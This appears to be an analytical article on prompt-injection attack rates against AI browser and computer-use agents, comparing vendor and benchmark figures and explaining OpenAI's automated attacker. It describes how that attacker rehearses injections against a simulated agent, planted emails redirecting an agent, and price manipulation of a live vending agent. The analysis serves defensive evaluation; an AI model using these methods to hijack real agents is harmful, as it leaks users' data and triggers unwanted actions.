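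In May, Anthropic also ran a more direct test, a week-long contest in which expert testers competed for prizes by attacking Opus 4.8 and other models without knowing which model they were facing. Four of the 12 scenarios involved a browser. Opus 4.8 did better than comparable models from other companies, even though Anthropic had left its added safeguards off. The July results don't include an equivalent test because the contest for Opus 5 was still in preparation when Anthropic published that model's card.

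### The arithmetic of repeated attempts

If each attempt at an attack succeeds independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in k attempts is 1 − (1 − p)ᵏ. With a success rate of 0.2%, the chance of at least one success in 15 attempts is 1 − 0.998¹⁵, or about 3%.

This prediction can be compared with real results from a benchmark by Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems for weaknesses. Gray Swan developed it with the UK AI Security Institute, the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation, and several model developers. It has 28 scenarios in coding, computer use and tool use, in which the attacker tries to make the agent do something harmful and irreversible, such as leaking private data or making a payment. The organisers chose the 1,130 attacks from a public competition, selecting ones that worked against several models.

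The table compares the rates in Anthropic's Opus 5 card with what the formula predicts.

| Model | One attempt | 15 attempts, if independent | 15 attempts, measured |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 37.6% | 20.0% |

Rounding could explain most of the gap for Opus 5, because a true rate of 0.15% would give a prediction of 2.2%. Rounding can't explain the gap for GPT-5.6 Sol.

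The formula overestimates the attacker's success over repeated attempts because attempts in the same scenario aren't independent. They share a task, a page and a model, so some scenarios are easy for the attacker and others are nearly hopeless. Suppose that every attack succeeds in 2 out of 100 scenarios and none succeeds in the other 98. The success rate is 2% per attempt, and after 15 attempts in each scenario the attacker has succeeded in only two scenarios. If each attempt had an independent 2% chance, the attacker would succeed in about 26.

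Anthropic's browser results have the same pattern. Attacks on Opus 5 succeeded in 3.70% of attempts, and at least one of the ten attempts succeeded in 11 of the 129 scenarios. If every attempt had been equally likely to succeed, that number would have been about 40.

This clustering also changes the comparison between Opus 5 and Sonnet 5. Opus 5 looks four times as vulnerable when measured by attempts (3.70% against 0.93%), but the two models are close in the number of scenarios in which an attack succeeded, at 11 and 9. Opus 5 failed about 48 times across its 11 scenarios, so the attacks that worked on it succeeded in more than four attempts out of ten on average. Sonnet 5 failed only 12 times across its 9 scenarios, which means a successful attack usually worked just once.

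If an attack with a 0.2% chance of success reaches 10,000 agents, it will succeed an average of 20 times, whether or not the attempts are independent. But the 0.2% figure is an average over many attacks, and a criminal can choose the most reliable one. In a scenario where an attack works 40% of the time, it would succeed about 4,000 times against the same number of agents, unless the developer noticed and blocked it first.

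Repeated attempts make an attack more likely to succeed, even when successes cluster in certain scenarios. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that, on an older Gray Swan benchmark, attacks on Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. If each attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the rates would have been about 38% with ten attempts and 99% with 100. This estimate is close for ten attempts but much too high for 100, probably because attackers had already succeeded in the easy scenarios by then and the hard ones remained.

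An adaptive attacker can learn from each failure, so later attempts may be more likely to succeed than earlier ones. A formula based on the first attempt could therefore underestimate the risk.

### What zero in 129 leaves open

With safeguards on, no attack on Opus 5 succeeded in any of the 129 scenarios. If an attacker could break a true share r of scenarios, the chance of that result would be (1 − r)¹²⁹. That chance is about 27% if r is 1%, so the result wouldn't be surprising, but only 5% if r is 2.3%. At the usual 95% confidence level, the test therefore rules out a share above roughly 2% to 3%, depending on how one calculates the limit.

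Using the 1,290 attempts instead would make the limit too low, at about 0.2%, because we learn much less from ten attempts in one scenario than from attempts in ten different scenarios. The formula in the previous section failed for the same reason.

The limit of 2% to 3% is also valid only for a random sample of the attacks that Opus 5 will face, and the scenarios aren't one. The limit may be too high, because professionals designed the attacks and most hostile text on the web is much cruder. But it may also be too low, because the testers had adapted the attacks to Opus 4.7, and nothing in Anthropic's description suggests that they could watch the July safeguards block an attack and then try again.

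An attack success rate of zero often seems to reflect the limits of the test rather than of what attackers can do. In February 2026, attackers had no success against Claude Opus 4.6 in a coding test, even with 200 attempts, according to VentureBeat. For the Opus 4.8 card in May, Anthropic worked with Gray Swan to train a stronger automated attacker, because the existing one couldn't find successful attacks on its latest models. The new attacker succeeded in 23 of 40 coding scenarios against Opus 4.8 with thinking on and safeguards off. The success rate in the browser also jumped from almost nothing to 31.5%.

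The July result is still good evidence that the safeguards work. Mythos 5 failed in 71 of the 129 scenarios without them and in none with them. The model was the same, so the safeguards must have stopped attacks that would otherwise have succeeded.

The safeguards in this test, which Anthropic calls auto mode, pair a scanner with an action checker. Anthropic describes the two as failing independently, a claim that calls for the same caution as the assumption that attempts are independent. If each layer missed 10% of attacks and their mistakes were unrelated, only 1% would get past both. But an instruction that closely resembles the user's request may look harmless to the scanner and lead to an action that looks harmless to the checker. Such shared mistakes could bring the combined miss rate much closer to 10%.

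The safeguards were less effective in Anthropic's computer-use tests, where Claude operates a graphical interface and only the scanning layer was on. For Opus 4.8, scanning lowered the success rate from 7.14% to 5.11% of attempts. With 200 attempts per scenario, the attacker succeeded at least once in 8 of 14 scenarios with scanning and 7 without it. The extra scenario came from a single success in 200 attempts, so scanning probably didn't make things worse, but it didn't stop a persistent attacker either. Against Opus 5, the attacker succeeded in only one of the 14 scenarios, with or without scanning.

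Safeguards that lower the attack rate can also block legitimate work. Anthropic says that Opus 4.8 with safeguards was slightly easier to attack in coding than Opus 4.7, but considers this a better balance because Opus 4.8 mistakes fewer harmless texts for attacks. The browser rates don't show how many ordinary tasks auto mode interrupted. Someone comparing two agents would want that number too, since an agent that refused every task would have an attack rate of zero.

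### How OpenAI's automated attacker works

OpenAI uses a language model to search for new attacks. It trained the model for this with reinforcement learning, a method that rewards a model when its attempts succeed. It chose this method partly because a serious attack on a browser agent can take many steps, and the attacker may find out only at the end whether the agent sent the email or made the bank transfer.

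In the version that OpenAI described in December 2025, the attacker could rehearse before committing to an attack.

1. The attacker writes a text to plant, such as an email.
2. A simulator runs the browser agent as it would behave if it came across the text.
3. The simulator returns a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions.
4. The attacker uses the record to revise the text, and repeats the process several times.

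The record of the agent's full reasoning gives this attacker an advantage over outsiders, who can't see it. The attacker found attacks that led the agent through tens or even hundreds of steps, and some strategies that OpenAI's human testers had missed. One was the planted email that made Atlas send a resignation letter. OpenAI's account doesn't give a success rate for Atlas, so it shows that such attacks existed but not how often they worked.

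In July 2026, OpenAI's *GPT-Red* introduced a stronger successor. OpenAI trained GPT-Red alongside a group of defending models. GPT-Red earned a reward when its attack worked, and the defenders earned one when they resisted the attack and still completed their task. As the defenders improved, GPT-Red had to find new attacks. OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6.

OpenAI tested GPT-Red against GPT-5.1 in a copy of the contest behind Gray Swan's benchmark. GPT-Red found a successful attack in 84% of the scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. In November 2025, Anthropic wrote that human researchers consistently beat automated systems at finding creative attacks. OpenAI's result suggests that this is no longer always true, at least against an older model and with an attacker trained on an unusually large amount of computing power.

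If a strong automated attacker such as GPT-Red can break six times as many scenarios as people can, tests based on human attacks, including Anthropic's 129 browser scenarios, may greatly underestimate how often attacks can succeed. SiliconANGLE (2026) reports that GPT-Red is itself weak at attacks that unfold over several exchanges and limited in its use of instructions hidden in images. The image limitation could matter for agents that work from screenshots.

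OpenAI also tried GPT-Red on a live AI agent that ran a vending machine in its office. After practising on a close simulation, GPT-Red attacked the live agent and achieved all three of its goals, including cutting the price of an expensive item to $0.50 and cancelling another customer's order.

Anthropic argues that its own tests are harsher than reality, because real attackers don't know exactly how the target works and risk detection if they try repeatedly. The vending machine example shows that attackers can reduce that risk by practising in private and using only the finished attack in public. GPT-Red had a description of the system and could watch the simulated agent's tool calls, advantages a criminal might not have. But anyone with a subscription can practise on their own copy of a commercial browser agent.

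### OpenAI's figures for its own models

OpenAI reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed against 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct prompt injections. That figure covers only direct injections, in which the user tries to override the developer's instructions. Indirect injections, which are planted in web pages or emails, matter more for a browser agent. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gives an average success rate of 3.77% for indirect attacks on Sol, about 75 times the direct rate.

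OpenAI reports that GPT-6 Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect attacks in the same series of tests, so 0.21% succeeded. Sol resisted 96.23%. These figures are averages over OpenAI's test tasks, with no separate rate for browsers. The closest OpenAI came to a browser rate in July was reporting that its latest model scored more than 97% on several tests of indirect attacks in developer tools and browsing.

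One reason for caution is that OpenAI uses GPT-Red both to train its models and to test them. OpenAI keeps the test environments out of training, but a model may still become especially good at resisting GPT-Red's style of attack. The results for the three versions of GPT-5.6 are consistent with this.

| Model | OpenAI's indirect tests, average success rate | Gray Swan, success within 15 attempts |
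|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.77% | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 3.32% | 30.4% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 2.94% | 43.9% |

Luna was the hardest model to attack in OpenAI's tests and the easiest in Gray Swan's. The first column covers single attempts and the second covers 15 attempts, but that difference alone is unlikely to reverse the order. The two tests probably measure different weaknesses, so a buyer who saw only one set of results could choose a model that does poorly on the other test.

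Astra, with its safeguards on, also faced Gray Swan's attacks in an outside test. Within 15 attempts, 8.5% of attacks succeeded against Astra and 27.0% against Sol. Astra's figure implies that a single attempt succeeds roughly 0.6% of the time or more, about three times the rate in OpenAI's own tests. Astra clearly did better than Sol in both sets of tests.

### Can anyone compare the makers?

Astra's 8.5% and Opus 5's 2.0% both come from Gray Swan, but they aren't directly comparable because OpenAI reported Astra's rate on a larger set of 1,810 attacks, which included newer ones. The larger set seems to be harder, since Sol's rate was 20.0% on the smaller set and 27.0% on the larger one. Opus 5 would probably still have a lower rate than Astra, because its rate on the smaller set was a tenth of Sol's, while Astra's on the larger set was almost a third of Sol's. Opus 5 also ran without its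 added safeguards. This is an estimate until someone tests both models on the same attacks, and neither set measures browser use separately.

The comparison may also be out of date, because Anthropic has since released newer models, including Claude Fable 5.1. The results for Mythos 5 are a reason not to assume that the newer models' rates are lower.

In mid-2026, VentureBeat compared what four developers had disclosed and found that only Anthropic had published a success rate for browser attacks.

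- OpenAI gave GPT-5.5 a score of 0.963 for resisting known attacks through connectors, down from 0.998 for an earlier model.
- Google said that Gemini 3 was more resistant but gave no number.
- Meta tested its protective software on the AgentDojo benchmark, where it reduced successful attacks from 17.6% to 1.75%. This measures the software rather than a browser product.

OpenAI has published much more since then, including figures for GPT-5.6 and Astra. The Opus 5 card includes Gray Swan's results for Gemini 3.1 Pro, but Anthropic warns that Gemini's rate isn't comparable, because people had attacked that model directly in the competition that supplied the attacks.

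Claude has the highest published number in VentureBeat's comparison, but it isn't necessarily the riskiest choice, because a company that publishes no browser rate may have a better agent or a worse one. Anthropic deserves credit for reporting results that made its own model look bad, and a buyer could reasonably ask the other makers for the same information.

Independent researchers have found much higher rates in released browsers. For example, Atlas and Comet leaked data in roughly two-thirds of runs in cross-site tests by Wang and colleagues. Those tests used older models and pairs of pages chosen because a leak was possible. They also measured whole products as people used them. The gap between these results and a developer's near-zero rates is due partly to progress and partly to the choice of test. Separating the two would require running both tests on the same product.

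Spreadsheet agents are even harder to judge from these numbers. Anthropic's two 2026 cards give rates for coding, tool use, computer use and browsers, but no separate rate for Claude for Excel. We can't calculate one from PromptArmor's demonstrations either, because PromptArmor didn't report how many attempts failed.

The browser rate is not a reliable estimate for spreadsheets. In the browser test, hostile text reached Claude through screenshots and page contents, and auto mode checked Claude's actions. In a workbook, the result would depend on whether the add-in's checks recognise a dangerous formula. A useful test would plant instructions in imported sheets, give the agent ordinary requests such as comparing two sets of figures, and count how often private data reached an outside server. It would also need to report the number of attempts, the model and the approval settings, because each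 changed the outcome in PromptArmor's cases or in the browser tests.
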